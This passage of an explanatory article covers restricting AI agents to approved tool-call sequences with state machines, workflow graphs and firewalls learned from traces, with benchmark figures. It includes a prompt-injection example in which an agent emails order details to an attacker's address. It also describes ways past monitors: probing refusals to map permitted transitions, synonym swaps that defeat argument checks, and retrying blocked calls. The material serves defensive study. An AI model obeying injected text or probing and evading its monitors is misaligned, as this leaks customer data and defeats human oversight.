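# Restricting AI agents to approved sequences of actions with state machines and typed workflow graphs

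## How agents act through tools, and what a rule about order adds

An AI agent is a language model that software runs in a loop. The model proposes an action, receives the result and proposes again. Agents send emails, change bookings, issue payments and edit code. One way to constrain them is to restrict the order of their actions. Software outside the model tracks what the agent has done and allows only the next steps that a written rule permits. The rule can be a state machine, a set of states with labelled transitions in which the current state determines which actions may come next. It can also be a workflow graph, a plan of steps that a developer fixes before the agent starts. These methods predate language models. They come from computer security, where engineers were working out how to contain untrusted programs in the early 1970s, and from runtime verification, the branch of computer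 science that checks running programs against formal rules.

### The loop and the trace

A language model produces only text. To act, it writes a tool call, a structured request to run a named function with given arguments. Anthropic's developer documentation for the Claude models, *How tool use works*, describes the cycle. The application sends the model the user's message and a list of tools with the arguments each one takes. The model replies with a request to use one or more of them. The application extracts the function name and arguments, runs the function (a database query, say, or a payment) and sends the conversation back with the result appended. The model then requests another tool or finishes. The model "never runs anything on its own," as Anthropic puts it, so ordinary code in the application can refuse a call before running it.

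A trace is the ordered list of tool calls and results in one run. *Enforcing Benign Trajectories* (Dang, 2026) defines it as a finite sequence (t₁, p₁), …, (tₖ, pₖ), where tᵢ is the name of the tool at step i and pᵢ its arguments. *Enforcing Temporal Constraints for LLM Agents* (Kamath, Zhang and colleagues, 2025) also includes what each call returned and the state of the tools at the time, because many rules depend on those values. A policy is a rule that sorts traces into permitted and forbidden ones. (In reinforcement learning, the same word means an agent's learned decision function.) *Sapien* (Tiffany, Zhang and colleagues, 2026), which describes a policy engine from Google, defines the ideal policy for a task as one that permits every appropriate trace and rejects all others.

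### A shop's support agent

Suppose an online shop gives its support agent four tools. `verify_customer` compares an email address and postcode with the shop's records and returns a customer number. `read_order` returns an order's contents, price, owner and delivery notes. `issue_refund` pays back a stated amount on a stated order. `send_email` writes to any address, since the agent also corresponds with couriers and suppliers. The shop has these rules:

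- Verify the customer before reading an order.
- Refund an order at most once, and never above its price.
- Email order details only to the verified customer.

Test suites for agents contain similar rules. The retail policy in *τ-Voice* (2026), a benchmark for voice agents, requires the agent to authenticate the user at the start of a conversation, even if the user has already supplied an ID, and to serve only one user per conversation. Agents do break such rules. In a test by Kamath and colleagues, a customer asked to return a camera, and the agent immediately looked up the order and disclosed its details without authenticating the customer, even though a second language model was screening its behaviour.

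That agent skipped a step. The shop's agent can also do harm without skipping any, as in this trace, a double refund:

```
verify_customer("ana@example.com", "N1 7AA")  → customer 17
read_order(1042)                              → owner 17, price £60
issue_refund(1042, £60)                       → no reply
issue_refund(1042, £60)                       → refunded
```

The payment service had carried out the earlier request, but its reply got lost on the way back. The agent tried again, and the shop paid out £120 on a £60 order. Nobody attacked anything. In the next trace, a leaked order, somebody did:

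```
verify_customer("ana@example.com", "N1 7AA")      → customer 17
read_order(1042)                                  → owner 17, address, delivery note
send_email("claims@example.net", order details)   → sent
```

An attacker had planted a sentence in the delivery note asking for the full order details to be sent to that address "to settle a claim". This is prompt injection, where text in data the agent reads makes it follow an attacker's instructions.

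### Why checks on single calls miss these cases

Both traces pass a permission list, which names the tools an agent may use. Such lists apply the principle of least privilege. Saltzer and Schroeder stated this principle for computing in general in *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* (1975), writing that a program should operate with "the least set of privileges necessary to complete the job". The support agent's job includes refunds and emails, so all four tools belong on its list.

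A finer check also looks at the call's arguments, so it might refuse refunds above £100 or malformed addresses. It still ignores everything that came before the call. The two requests in the double refund are identical, so the check must allow both or neither, and if it allows neither, Ana never gets her money. The leaked order poses the same problem. Emailing the details of order 1042 to ana@example.com is right in a conversation where Ana has passed verification and wrong in one where the agent is serving somebody else, but the check can't distinguish the two because the call is the same.

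Tiffany and colleagues illustrate this with a personal assistant whose user asks it to refund "the person who sent me money last week". The tightest permission list allows the tools for listing transactions and sending money, so the agent can still send any sum to any account. Limits set in advance on the recipient and amount do not help much either. The agent learns the right values only by reading the transaction history, so the policy has to refer to what an earlier call returned.

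The shop's database can record each refund so that `issue_refund` itself rejects a repeat. This is good engineering, and it works for facts the shop stores anyway. But a database won't hold facts about the run, such as who has passed verification in this conversation and what the agent has read since, unless some component records them. A component that records these facts and checks that record before each call is already checking the sequence.

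How often order matters depends on the rules in force. *LEANGUARD* (Sankar, Ganguly and colleagues, 2026) tested a program that checks every proposed tool call against a formally specified policy. The tests used five Qwen models of up to 27 billion parameters on τ²-bench, a set of simulated customer-service conversations. The program stopped 1,702 calls, and 411 of them, about a quarter, lacked a required earlier step. In most of these, the agent had not yet authenticated the customer or read the record it was about to change. Two rules stricter than the benchmark's accounted for 164 of the 411. The paper classified another 338 calls as missing authorisation because the customer had not confirmed the change, though confirmation is also an earlier step.

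Other policies can be enforced without a record of earlier calls. In *AgentPolicyForge*, Shang, Du and colleagues (2026) built 1,374 test episodes around rules such as limits on amounts and access only to one's own records. Every violation used a permitted tool, so a list of permitted tools would have caught none of them, but each could be detected from the arguments, resources and current state of a single call. A rule about order therefore supplements checks on single calls, and a shop would want both. According to *AgentTrust* (2026), most guardrails in production still examine one call at a time. In Dang's tests, up to 75 percent of attacks made up of individually harmless calls got past one such firewall.

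### Why an instruction in the prompt is not enforcement

The shop could instead write its rules into the agent's prompt, but that would not enforce them. Enforcement means preventing a forbidden action before it has any effect, and a prompt only changes how likely the model is to propose that action. If the model proposes the call anyway, the application runs it.

The model also receives its rules through the same channel as everything else. *Prompt injection is not SQL injection*, from Britain's National Cyber Security Centre (NCSC), explains why this is a problem. In SQL injection, an older attack, text from a web form runs as a database command. Programmers can stop it by passing commands and data separately, but language models inherently make no such distinction. The shop's rule and the sentence in the delivery note both arrive as text from which the model predicts more text. The NCSC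 therefore believes injection may never be "totally mitigated", as quoted in ITPro's *NCSC issues urgent warning over growing AI prompt injection risks*.

Rules in the prompt do have a large effect. Shang and colleagues gave Claude Sonnet 5 requests designed to make it break a policy. Without the policy in its prompt, the model executed a tool call that violated the policy in more than 98 percent of these episodes. With the policy in its prompt, it did so in 13 to 15 percent, but it also refused about 9 percent of legitimate requests.

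Agents do worse with longer rulebooks. *HANDBOOK.md* (Panavas, Minus and colleagues, 2026) placed agents in simulated companies with handbooks of 20 to 124 pages. The best of thirty model configurations met every requirement in 36.2 percent of trials. The failures include unfinished work as well as forbidden acts, so the failure rate overstates rule-breaking. In one case, the handbook named two people who could authorise a dismissal, and a vice-president who was not one of them ordered a dismissal by email. GPT-5.5 searched for written authorisation from the two named people, found none and processed the dismissal anyway. The agent had the rule and ran the check, but nothing in the loop made the next call depend on the result.

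Models have become much harder to hijack. The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection* reports that attacks on Anthropic's Opus 5 as a browser agent failed in all 129 test scenarios. It also reports that in a broader test by the security firm Gray Swan, attackers succeeded 2.0 percent of the time after 15 attempts. Operators have good reason to prefer such a model, but these results cover only the attacks that were tested. They also don't apply to the double refund or the unauthorised dismissal, which involved no attacker.

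### The reference monitor

The bare loop lacks what computer security calls a reference monitor. Anderson (1972) proposed this mechanism in *Computer Security Technology Planning Study*, a report for the US Air Force. It checks every attempt by a program to use data, devices or other programs against a list of what that program may do. An agent's equivalent would be a component outside the model that checks every relevant tool call before the call takes effect. Anderson required that the monitor be tamper-proof, that the system always invoke it, and that it be small enough for people to analyse and test completely. One commercial operating system of the day, at 200,000 to 300,000 instructions, was too large to meet the third requirement. A language model cannot serve as the monitor for another one under that requirement, because nobody can test it completely. A table of states and transitions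 for the shop would fit on a page, which is small enough for people to analyse and test in full.

Saltzer and Schroeder added two principles that apply directly to agents. Complete mediation requires a check on every access to every object. Fail-safe defaults forbid anything the rules do not explicitly permit. They chose this default because a mistake in a rule that grants access usually causes a refusal that somebody notices, while a mistake in a rule that excludes access silently allows it.

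With a record of the run, a monitor can also apply least privilege at each step. The support agent needs `issue_refund` to do its job, but not before it has verified the customer, or again for an order it has already refunded. A rule about order can limit the tool to the steps where the agent needs it, while a permission list grants it for the whole conversation.

### What to ask of any mechanism

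Mechanisms differ in what rules they can express. A rule language limited to tool names can require `verify_customer` before `read_order`, but it cannot compare a refund with a price. Checking tool calls cannot enforce every requirement. The benchmark retail policy in *τ-Voice* forbids the agent from making up information or giving subjective recommendations, and an agent can do either without calling a tool. Sankar and colleagues therefore formalised only the part of the τ²-bench policies that a check on tool calls can enforce, producing 45 rules. Tiffany and colleagues also note that no exact rule can determine whether an email faithfully summarises a document.

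Sankar and colleagues proved that their monitor allows a call only if the call satisfies the written policy. They note that this protects people only if the monitor receives true information about the environment and every consequential call passes through it. Applications do not always meet the second condition by default. For example, Anthropic runs some tools, such as web search, on its own servers, and the application usually learns of those calls only after they have finished.

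Monitors can also reduce utility, the share of legitimate tasks that the agent still completes. A monitor that refused everything would stop every attack, so an attack success rate means little without the utility figure. On DTap, a benchmark for prompt injection, Sankar and colleagues cut the success rate of direct attacks from 57.9 to 5.9 percent, but their deployment permitted no changes to any record, and utility fell from 53.1 to 12.5 percent. On τ²-bench, where the policy allowed changes, utility fell much less. It went from 72.7 to 68.9 percent when the agent was told only that its call had not run, and to 70.9 percent when the refusal also named the broken rule and gave a hint.

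Refusing a tool call can raise task success, because a forbidden write often makes the task fail. In *Reason Less, Verify More* (2026), four fixed checks on an inexpensive model's tool calls raised task success from 29.6 to 42.0 percent, and a replication found nearly the same gain. Most of the improvement came from tasks in which a check blocked a call, where success rose from 13.8 to 33.1 percent. The change in the remaining tasks could have been due to chance.

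## State machines that decide which tool may be called next

A reference monitor that enforces order has to track what the agent has done. A state machine records this in its current state. A developer can write the machine's transition table by hand, or software can learn one from recorded runs.

### States, guards and registers

Formally, a machine for tool calls has five parts:

- a finite set Q of states
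- a start state q₀
- a set T of tool names
- a set R of registers, which are variables that save values from earlier calls
- a transition function δ, which assigns a guard g and an update u to a state q and a tool t

A guard g is a condition on the arguments x of a proposed call and the current register values v. In state q, the monitor permits the call t(x) if δ(q, t) exists and g(v, x) is true. Once the call has run and returned a result r, u(v, x, r) gives the next state and the new register values. The function δ is partial, meaning that some pairs of state and tool have no entry, and the monitor denies any call whose pair has no entry. This follows Saltzer and Schroeder's principle of fail-safe defaults.

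Computer scientists call this a register automaton. *What Can Be Enforced?* (Ray, 2026) defines a version for agents that also has counters. *Soteria* (He, Desai and colleagues, 2026) uses nearly the same structure for an agent's plan, with "plan variables" as the registers.

The machine below implements the shop's three rules for a conversation about one order. It has four registers: `customer`, `address`, `order` and `price`.

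| State | Permitted call | Guard | What follows |
|---|---|---|---|
| Start | `verify_customer(a, z)` | none | If the details match, save `customer` and `address` and go to Verified. Otherwise stay. |
| Start, Verified | `send_email(a, text)` | none | Stay. |
| Verified | `read_order(n)` | none | If the owner is `customer`, save `order` and `price` and go to Order open. Otherwise go to Closed. |
| Order open | `issue_refund(n, x)` | n = `order` and 0 < x ≤ `price` | Go to Refund sent. |
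| Order open, Refund sent | `send_email(a, text)` | a = `address` | Stay. |

`read_order` has two possible next states because a guard runs before the call and cannot use its result. The monitor can check who owns an order only after the call returns the order's details. If the order belongs to somebody else, the monitor moves to Closed, where the agent can't call any tools.

The next table runs a permitted trace and the double refund through the machine. The two traces begin with the same two calls.

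| Trace | Call | State before | Check | State after | `order` | `price` |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Both | `verify_customer("ana@example.com", "N1 7AA")` | Start | no guard | Verified | empty | empty |
| Both | `read_order(1042)` | Verified | no guard | Order open | 1042 | £60 |
| Permitted | `issue_refund(1042, £60)`, refunded | Order open | order matches, £60 ≤ £60 | Refund sent | 1042 | £60 |
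| Permitted | `send_email("ana@example.com", …)` | Refund sent | address matches | Refund sent | 1042 | £60 |
| Forbidden | `issue_refund(1042, £60)`, no reply | Order open | order matches, £60 ≤ £60 | Refund sent | 1042 | £60 |
| Forbidden | `issue_refund(1042, £60)` | Refund sent | no transition, so denied | Refund sent | 1042 | £60 |

The machine also blocks the email that would leak the order, because claims@example.net differs from the saved address. But it can't detect whether an email contains order details, so after `read_order` it denies every email to anyone but Ana, including a harmless question to the courier. Its state is also lost when the conversation ends. To prevent a second refund tomorrow, `read_order` would have to return past refunds so that the machine could go straight to Refund sent.

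### Why plain states run out

Suppose Ana has ten orders and may ask for a refund on any of them. A machine without registers needs a separate state for each combination of refunded and unrefunded orders. That is 2¹⁰ = 1,024 states for ten orders and more than a million for twenty. The developer would also need to know the order numbers in advance and add states for every possible price.

Saved values avoid this. The shop can replace `order` and `price` with two lists indexed by order number, `price[n]` and `refunded[n]`. Reading an order fills in its price and sets `refunded[n]` to 0. A refund of x on order n requires that `refunded[n]` is 0 and x is at most `price[n]`, and it sets `refunded[n]` to 1. Order open and Refund sent merge into one state, so the machine has four states however many orders Ana has. The ten `refunded` entries can still take 1,024 combinations of values, but nobody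 has to write those out or review them.

If the shop allows partial refunds, it needs a running total for each order instead of a yes or no. Ray gives a similar example, a daily cap on transfers to each recipient, which needs one counter for each pair of recipient and day. A fixed set of registers can't keep these totals, since registers only store and compare values. But counters make a policy harder to analyse. Ray proves that once a policy may have two counters that can go down as well as up, no algorithm can decide in every case whether the policy is trivial. An algorithm can decide this for a restricted class of policies whose counters only rise, and Ray notes that ordinary caps, quotas and rate limits need only rising counters. Anderson wanted a monitor that people could analyse completely, which is a reason to stay within that class.

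### The loop around the machine

At run time, the monitor does the following with each proposed call:

```
if δ(q, t) does not exist:   deny
(g, u) = δ(q, t)
if g(v, x) is false:         deny
r = run t(x)
(q, v) = u(v, x, r)
return r to the model
```

Written this way, the loop allows the double refund. The payment service's reply never arrives, the update never runs, and the machine is still in Order open when the agent tries again. For a payment, the monitor has to save the new state before it sends the call, and restore the old one only if the service confirms that it paid nothing. *Soteria*'s strict mode does the opposite and leaves the state unchanged after a network timeout so that the model can retry. That rule suits a lookup, but in the shop it would let the agent refund Ana twice. Parallel calls cause a similar problem. If the model requests two refunds at once, the monitor has to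 update the state for one before it checks the other, or both will pass.

In an example of the strict mode from He and colleagues, a customer wants to cancel a flight reservation. The policy requires the agent to check first that the customer has not flown any part of it. The model looks up the reservation and then tries to cancel it. The current state has no transition for cancelling, so the software blocks the call and returns an error that lists the available actions. The model runs the missing check, and the cancellation goes through after another check on the booking's age.

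The same paper shows a drawback of denial by default. A customer asks the agent to cancel one reservation and look up another. At the cancelling step, the plan permits only the cancellation, so strict mode blocks the lookup even though it is harmless. *Soteria* therefore also has a guided mode, which shows the model the plan as a flowchart but lets it choose any tool, while a separate monitor checks each call against the written rules. In this mode the lookup runs because it breaks no rule.

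### What to do after a denial

The monitor can stop the run, return an error and keep the state, or ask a person.

Stopping makes sense when the monitor's information is no longer reliable. *Soteria* aborts if a tool's result contradicts the tool's specification, for example if it shows a cancelled reservation as still active. The plan's safety checks depend on the tool working as specified. Stopping after an ordinary denial, however, leaves the customer with a half-finished task.

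Returning an error when a tool call is blocked lets the agent recover. Statewright (2026), a state-machine tool for coding agents, returns an error that names the blocked tool, the current phase, the available tools and the call that would advance the workflow. Its developer, Ben Cochran, who presented it in a *Show HN* post on the forum Hacker News, reports that even small models usually change their approach instead of repeating the blocked call. If the agent does repeat the call, Statewright gives the same answer because the state has not changed, whereas a language model acting as the judge might answer differently.

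When a state machine refuses a tool call, it should return the error to the agent in the same turn. Zhang, Kweon and Han (2026), in *How Strongly Should Task State Influence an LLM Agent?*, had agents work through simulated projects while a gate refused steps that were out of order. When the gate reported a refusal only on the next turn, a smaller model's replies implied in 70 of 86 cases that the work had been done. When the notice came in the same turn, this happened in none of 89 cases, and task success did not change.

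In He and colleagues' tests, agents recovered well on customer-service tasks. On 50 airline tasks, adding the monitor to the guided plan raised GPT-5.4-mini's completion rate from 54 to 60 percent, a difference of three tasks, and left Gemini 3 Flash's at 62 percent. Violations fell from 12 and 22, respectively, to zero. The design guarantees this result because the same rules blocked the calls and scored the runs. On longer file and document tasks, Claude Opus 4.6's completion rate was lower with *Soteria* (18.6 percent) than with no guard (30.2 percent), although only 11.6 percent of the unguarded runs both finished the task and broke no rule.

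LEANGUARD, Sankar and colleagues' policy checker, can also replace a denied call with a corrected one and prove that the correction satisfies the policy.

A person should decide when the rules can't settle a case, such as a goodwill refund above the price. *MarkovSim* (Lei, Chen and Zhang, 2026), a system for engineering simulations, has a separate state for asking a person. The agent enters this state when it is uncertain or when a step has failed a fixed number of times. The engineer can then grant more attempts, discuss the problem or end the run.

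### Hiding a tool or rejecting the call

The software can also leave a tool out of the list it sends to the model until the machine reaches a state that permits that tool. Statewright has used both methods. According to Cochran, the test program for small local models sent only the current phase's tools, while the plugin for Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, leaves every tool visible and blocks disallowed calls. Andrew's *Statewright Review* describes the tools as hidden in Claude Code too, but Cochran's own account contradicts this.

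Cochran prefers hiding tools where possible. A shorter list gives the model less text to process and fewer ways to choose badly, and Cochran attributes the measured gains to this. The drawback is cost, because model providers and local software reuse their computation for the unchanged part of a prompt, and a new tool list forces them to redo it. A simple workflow changes phase three to five times, but a long session with many changes could become noticeably more expensive.

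An application that hides tools from the model must still reject disallowed calls. The model can call a tool that is missing from its list, perhaps because the name came up earlier in the conversation. A list of tool names also can't express a guard. In the Order open state, `issue_refund` must be visible, so only a check on the arguments can stop a refund of £600. Hiding a tool may also lead the support agent to tell Ana that the shop doesn't offer refunds. The command-line program fsmp, which takes coding agents through workflows, avoids this problem by listing the blocked transitions and the reason for each.

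### Who advances the state

A state machine can enforce a rule only if the agent can't advance it just by claiming to have followed the rule. Suppose the shop's machine entered Verified whenever the agent said it had verified the customer. An agent that skipped the check, or that an attacker had persuaded to skip it, could say the same thing, and the machine would then permit the calls allowed after verification. A false claim can't advance the machine if it moves to Verified only when `verify_customer` returns a match from the shop's records.

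In fsmp, the agent reports its own progress. The program can block a transition until it has recorded two clean reviews, but according to its documentation, it can't verify that the agent's reports are true or force the agent to use the program at all. mcp-flowgate, another workflow tool, can require evidence such as passed tests, which it records as the steps run.

Zhang and colleagues measured how an agent's success depends on how strongly the recorded state constrains it. Their simulated user asked for the steps of a procurement project out of order, cancelled one and mentioned finished steps again. To succeed, an agent had to carry out every required step exactly once and do nothing else. Only an executed step could advance the recorded state, whatever the agent claimed in prose. With only the conversation, the model Qwen3-235B succeeded in 38 percent of 128 episodes. Adding an accurate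 checklist raised this to 55 percent, instructions each turn based on the state raised it to 84 percent, and a gate that refused forbidden steps raised it to 98 percent. When the model reasoned before each turn, it succeeded in 80 percent of episodes with the conversation alone and 95 percent with the gate, so the gate matters less for a stronger agent.

In another setup, the agent kept its own record of finished steps, which no software verified. It succeeded 70 percent of the time, more often than with the accurate checklist, but still repeated finished steps 21 to 27 times per 128 episodes. A self-reported state can therefore help an agent stay organised even when it is not safe to use for enforcement.

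The gate depends on its state being correct. Injecting an average of 0.8 errors per episode into the state cut success from 98 to 72 percent, and injecting 1.9 cut it to 41 percent. The gate also relied on a language model to match each request to a step, and rewording the requests cut success from 100 to 78 percent. The shop's machine avoids this second weakness because it reads tool names and arguments. Like the gate, though, it checks whether a step is allowed but not whether anyone asked for it. In a version of the test with real tools, a smaller model that received a request for a blocked step sometimes carried out the missing earlier steps unprompted and then the requested one, and the gate permitted each call.

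Statewright mixes the two ways of advancing. A typical bug-fixing workflow has a planning phase with read-only tools, an implementing phase with editing tools and a testing phase that allows shell commands only for running tests. In Claude Code, the software blocks edits during planning, but the model ends that phase itself by calling a transition tool and giving a reason. An agent that wants to edit can therefore declare that it is ready. The workflow that Andrew reproduces ends with a stricter condition, which lets the run complete only if a saved test result equals "pass". Andrew asserts that the engine, not the model, controls this value, but shows no code for it.

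Statewright advertises that models completed ten out of ten tasks with its tool and two out of ten without it. According to Andrew, these figures cover two local models on five tasks from SWE-bench, a collection of real software bugs. Cochran had not published the test program at launch, and the program hid tools, so the figures are weak evidence of how well the Claude Code plugin works. They also measure task completion rather than prevented harm. Later development has aimed at efficiency, and since version 0.3.0 each phase can also set the model, its reasoning level and a token budget, according to Statewright's announcement.

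PolicyGuide (Kang, Yu and Hwang, 2026) uses a second language model to track an agent's progress and keep it within company policy. Earlier systems such as StateFlow (2024), which represented a task as a finite-state machine whose states held prompts and tool calls, were designed mainly to complete the task. In PolicyGuide, GPT-5.4 first turns the policy into a graph of 104 to 158 nodes, which the researchers check by hand and then freeze. Before the agent answers each customer message, a verifier model works forward from the last recorded node, checking whether the conversation satisfies each node's condition. It accepts facts only from tool results, and choices and consent only from the customer's own messages. It stops at the first unsatisfied node and gives the agent instructions for the next step. Ordinary code stores the position in the graph and rejects nodes that don't exist.

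Kang and colleagues tested it on τ²-bench with GPT-5.4 as both agent and verifier, counting a task as solved only if all four attempts succeeded. The average score over three domains rose from 42 to 62 percent. Most of the gain came from telecom support, where the policy consists largely of ordered troubleshooting steps and the score rose from 19.3 to 61.4 percent. The airline score rose from 46 to 62 percent, and the retail score from 59.6 to 61.4 percent, though the retail difference could be chance. Guidance cost $0.34 to $0.56 per task and made conversations take more than five times as long.

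Two variants tested the graph and the outside verifier separately. On a smaller set of 40 telecom tasks, the full system solved 67.5 percent, compared with 35.0 percent when the verifier used the plain policy text instead of the graph. When the researchers put the graph in the agent's own prompt and removed the verifier, the agent completed permitted changes no better than an unguided agent in any domain. In retail, its overall score fell from 57.5 to 35.0 percent.

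The agent therefore can't advance PolicyGuide's state by claiming that a step is done, but it can still get past the gate. After each customer message, the software blocks the first unauthorised change to a record and runs the verifier again, then lets further attempts through until the customer next writes. Kang and colleagues call this mode advisory. When they forced agents in 13 saved conversations to retry a blocked change immediately, all 13 retries went through. Against customers who lied about their eligibility, the mode still cut the attack success rate from 20.0 to 8.7 percent. In the shop, such a gate could block the repeated refund, then let it through if the agent tried again before Ana replied.

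## Permitted sequences learned from recorded runs

The shop's developer wrote the transition table from the shop's rules. Software can also build such a table from logs of earlier runs. If one call followed another in the logs, the table permits that transition, and the monitor denies all others. This method needs no written policy, but the table describes what the agent usually does, which may differ from what the shop allows.

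### Profiles of Unix programs

The method comes from research on detecting break-ins. A Unix program makes a system call, a request to the operating system, whenever it reads a file, opens a network connection or starts another program. Forrest, Hofmeyr and colleagues (1996), in *A Sense of Self for Unix Processes*, recorded which calls normally follow one another in programs that run with administrator rights. Their software slides a window along the trace. With a window of four calls, it notes which calls come one, two and three places after each call. One of their examples is this trace:

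```
open, read, mmap, mmap, open, getrlimit, mmap, close
```

Here `read` or `getrlimit` may come one place after `open`, `mmap` two places after, and `mmap` or `close` three places after. If a new trace has `open` in place of the second `mmap`, four of its 18 pairs are missing from the table, a mismatch rate of 22 percent.

In the main test, the researchers sent 112 artificial messages to the mail program sendmail. These produced more than 1.5 million system calls but only about 1,500 distinct pairs with a window of six. Compared with a table of these pairs, other programs mismatched on roughly 5 to 32 percent of pairs, and successful attacks on sendmail on 0.3 to 4.2 percent.

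Forrest and colleagues analysed traces after the programs had run, so they detected attacks without preventing them. They ignored the arguments of calls and did not allow for changes in normal behaviour. They also expected to miss an intruder who used somebody else's account, because such an intruder makes only normal calls. Critics later pointed to false alarms and to mimicry attacks, in which the attacker makes an intrusion's calls look normal.

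The researchers expected programs to be consistent because their code is fixed. Agents turn out to be fairly regular too, even though the model chooses each call as it goes. In *Automata from Agent Traces*, Cho, Cardenoso Fernandez and colleagues (2026) built state machines from twelve sets of agent traces, using only the latest action as the state. Machines of 7 to 43 states could follow at least 99.7 percent of the steps in new traces. On τ²-bench, one machine built from the traces of four language models fitted each model's traces perfectly. The tools and tasks therefore seem to shape the order of actions more than the choice of model does, at least at this level of detail.

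### Building a machine from three traces

In April 2026, Dang applied the idea to blocking agents' tool calls. Dang's firewall, Praetor, builds a state machine from benign traces and checks each call against it before the call runs. A state consists of a tool and the tools called just before it. Each pair of consecutive calls in the traces adds an edge between two states, and each edge stores limits on the arguments seen there.

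Suppose the shop has three recorded runs:

```
1  verify_customer → read_order → send_email
2  verify_customer → read_order → issue_refund(£20) → send_email
3  verify_customer → read_order → issue_refund(£60) → issue_refund(£60) → send_email
```

In the third run, the payment service declined the first request and the agent rightly tried again. If each state includes one preceding tool, the traces give six states besides the start:

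| Tool | Preceding tool | Visits | Calls seen next |
|---|---|---|---|
| `verify_customer` | none | 3 | `read_order` (3) |
| `read_order` | `verify_customer` | 3 | `issue_refund` (2), `send_email` (1) |
| `issue_refund` | `read_order` | 2 | `send_email` (1), `issue_refund` (1) |
| `issue_refund` | `issue_refund` | 1 | `send_email` (1) |
| `send_email` | `issue_refund` | 2 | none |
| `send_email` | `read_order` | 1 | none |

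This machine denies `read_order` at the start of a conversation, although nobody wrote a rule about verification. It also permits the double refund. Dang's traces leave out results, so the machine can't distinguish a declined payment from a lost reply. Dang presents the tolerance of retries as a strength, which it is for web searches.

Praetor then prunes states with too few observations. With a threshold of two visits, it would remove both the second refund and the email that answered a question without a refund, because each occurred only once. It would treat them the same even though repeating the refund is dangerous and sending the email is harmless. Removing the second refund would also leave the other email state with only one visit, so the next pass would remove that state too, and the agent couldn't email anyone.

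Dang's default threshold is three, measured in transitions out of a state rather than visits to it. Taken literally, that rule deletes the last state of every trace, because no call follows it, and then deletes the earlier states, working backwards. A working version has to exempt final states.

The limits on arguments depend on their type:

- For a number, Praetor accepts the range seen in the logs plus some slack. The first refunds in the example were £20 and £60, so with 10 percent slack it would accept £18 to £66.
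- For an argument with a few fixed options, it accepts only values from the logs.
- For free text, it uses an embedding model, which turns text into a list of numbers so that texts with similar meanings lie close together. It accepts text that is close enough to the average of the logged examples.
- For arguments whose names match a list of sensitive patterns, such as file paths, it requires an exact match with a logged value.

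These limits check a call against other customers' runs rather than values saved earlier in the same run, so Praetor would accept a £60 refund on a £20 order and reject a legitimate £15 refund.

The leaked order shows the same weakness, because the agent calls the same three tools in the same order as in the first recorded run, and only the email address differs. An exact match would block every customer whose address is not in the logs, while a similarity check might accept an attacker's address that resembles a customer's. The handwritten machine avoids this choice by checking the recipient against Ana's saved address.

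### Results against a single-call checker

Dang compared Praetor with Aegis, a firewall that examines one call at a time (Yuan, Su and Zhao, 2026, *AEGIS*). Aegis extracts all the text from a call's arguments, searches it for 22 patterns associated with attacks, such as database commands hidden in a query, and then applies written policies. It can hold risky calls for a person to review. In the paper's own tests, Aegis blocked all 48 attacks and wrongly flagged 6 of 500 benign calls.

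The attacks in Dang's comparison came from Agent Security Bench, a test suite for attacks on agents, and the benign traces from ToolBench, a collection of tool-use tasks. The customer-service agent had 15 tools. Dang used 500 benign traces, keeping 100 of them for testing, and reports a machine of 450 states and 620 edges. In an average state, it permitted 1.8 of the 15 tools. Two other structured workflows covered operating-system tasks and database administration. Dang made 1,000 attempts with each of five types of attack in each workflow, with these average success rates:

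| Defence | Multi-step data theft | All five types |
|---|---|---|
| None | 89.5% | 79.0% |
| Aegis | 35.0% | 12.8% |
| Praetor | 0.0% | 2.2% |
| Praetor and Aegis together | 0.0% | 0.8% |

The largest gap is in multi-step data theft, where the order of calls matters most. But Praetor did not need a record of order to stop some of these attempts. In customer service, 42 percent of the attempts failed because they ended in a tool that never appeared in the benign traces, so a plain permission list would have stopped them. The share was 28 percent in database administration and 15 percent in the operating-system workflow. The remaining attempts used a known tool at the wrong point.

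Praetor did worse where tasks varied more. Attack success rose to 8.6 percent for a travel planner with 32 tools and 12.6 percent for a research assistant with 64. When an agent uses its tools in many different orders, the rules learned from its logs permit many different orders. Dang gives no Aegis figures for these two settings, so it is unclear whether Praetor still has the advantage there.

### Context length and changing tools

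Choosing how many preceding tools to include in each state involves a trade-off. Dang built attacks that make three normal calls before the harmful one. All of them succeeded when the state included one preceding tool, 45 percent succeeded with two, and none succeeded with three. The last result may depend partly on the openings being three calls long, since Dang does not report the same test with longer ones.

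Tracking more preceding tools also spreads the same traces over more states, so more legitimate states fall below the pruning threshold. With three preceding tools, 2.0 percent of benign tasks (two of 100, 95 percent confidence interval 0.2 to 7.0 percent) failed because Praetor blocked a call they needed. The failure rate rose to 3.2 percent with four preceding tools and 7.1 percent with five.

Increasing the number of traces tenfold, to 5,000, removed most of the false alarms and did little harm to security in this test. The share of benign tasks that failed fell to 0.2 percent, while overall attack success was 2.6 percent. Dang therefore recommends collecting several thousand traces before an operator turns on blocking.

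The profile also goes out of date. When Dang replaced a fifth of the agent's tools at random, 24.0 percent of benign tasks failed. To update the profile, a person reviews blocked calls, and the software adds the approved ones to the machine overnight. Praetor does not update itself from new behaviour without this review, because an attacker could then teach it to accept harmful sequences. After one update with 350 approved sequences, the failure rate was 3.8 percent. Dang estimates that the review takes an analyst 8.75 hours, or 90 seconds per sequence, which is short for a decision that permits the sequence in every later run.

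A handwritten table needs maintenance too, but its author can see which rules mention the new tool. In a learned table of 450 states, a missing transition usually goes unnoticed until a task fails.

### Attackers who test the boundary

An attacker who can make the agent attempt calls can learn from the refusals which transitions the state machine permits. Praetor keeps its state after a denial so the agent can recover, which also lets an attacker keep trying from the same state. In Dang's test, an automated search with 100 attempts per state found 88 percent of the permitted transitions, including routes to every sensitive tool the agent had. The same attacker then varied the arguments of harmful calls, and only 1.2 percent of the attacks succeeded.

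Dang concludes that the argument checks provide the main protection against such an attacker. The required order of actions is a larger obstacle for an attacker who doesn't know the machine. Dang attached 1,000 harmful endings to normal openings, and only 14 of the resulting traces followed a permitted sequence. The argument checks stopped all 14, but with so few cases, this result is compatible with as many as 23 percent of such attacks getting past the checks.

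The argument checks can also be evaded. When Dang replaced words in harmful arguments with synonyms, 18 percent of 500 variants passed, because the check measures similarity of meaning and synonyms barely change it. A different embedding model lowered the figure only to 16.5 percent. Requiring exact matches for sensitive arguments cut it to 0.4 percent, but only if the operator's list of those arguments is complete. Exact matching needs little or no memory of earlier calls, so against an attacker who can probe the system, Praetor relies mostly on a kind of check that a single-call firewall could also make.

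Some harmful runs contain only permitted steps. An agent allowed to read support tickets in a loop could read a hundred of them for an attacker, and each call would match the profile. Dang suggests limiting how often an agent may repeat such a loop. This requires a counter, and the operator has to choose its limit.

### How far the test can be trusted

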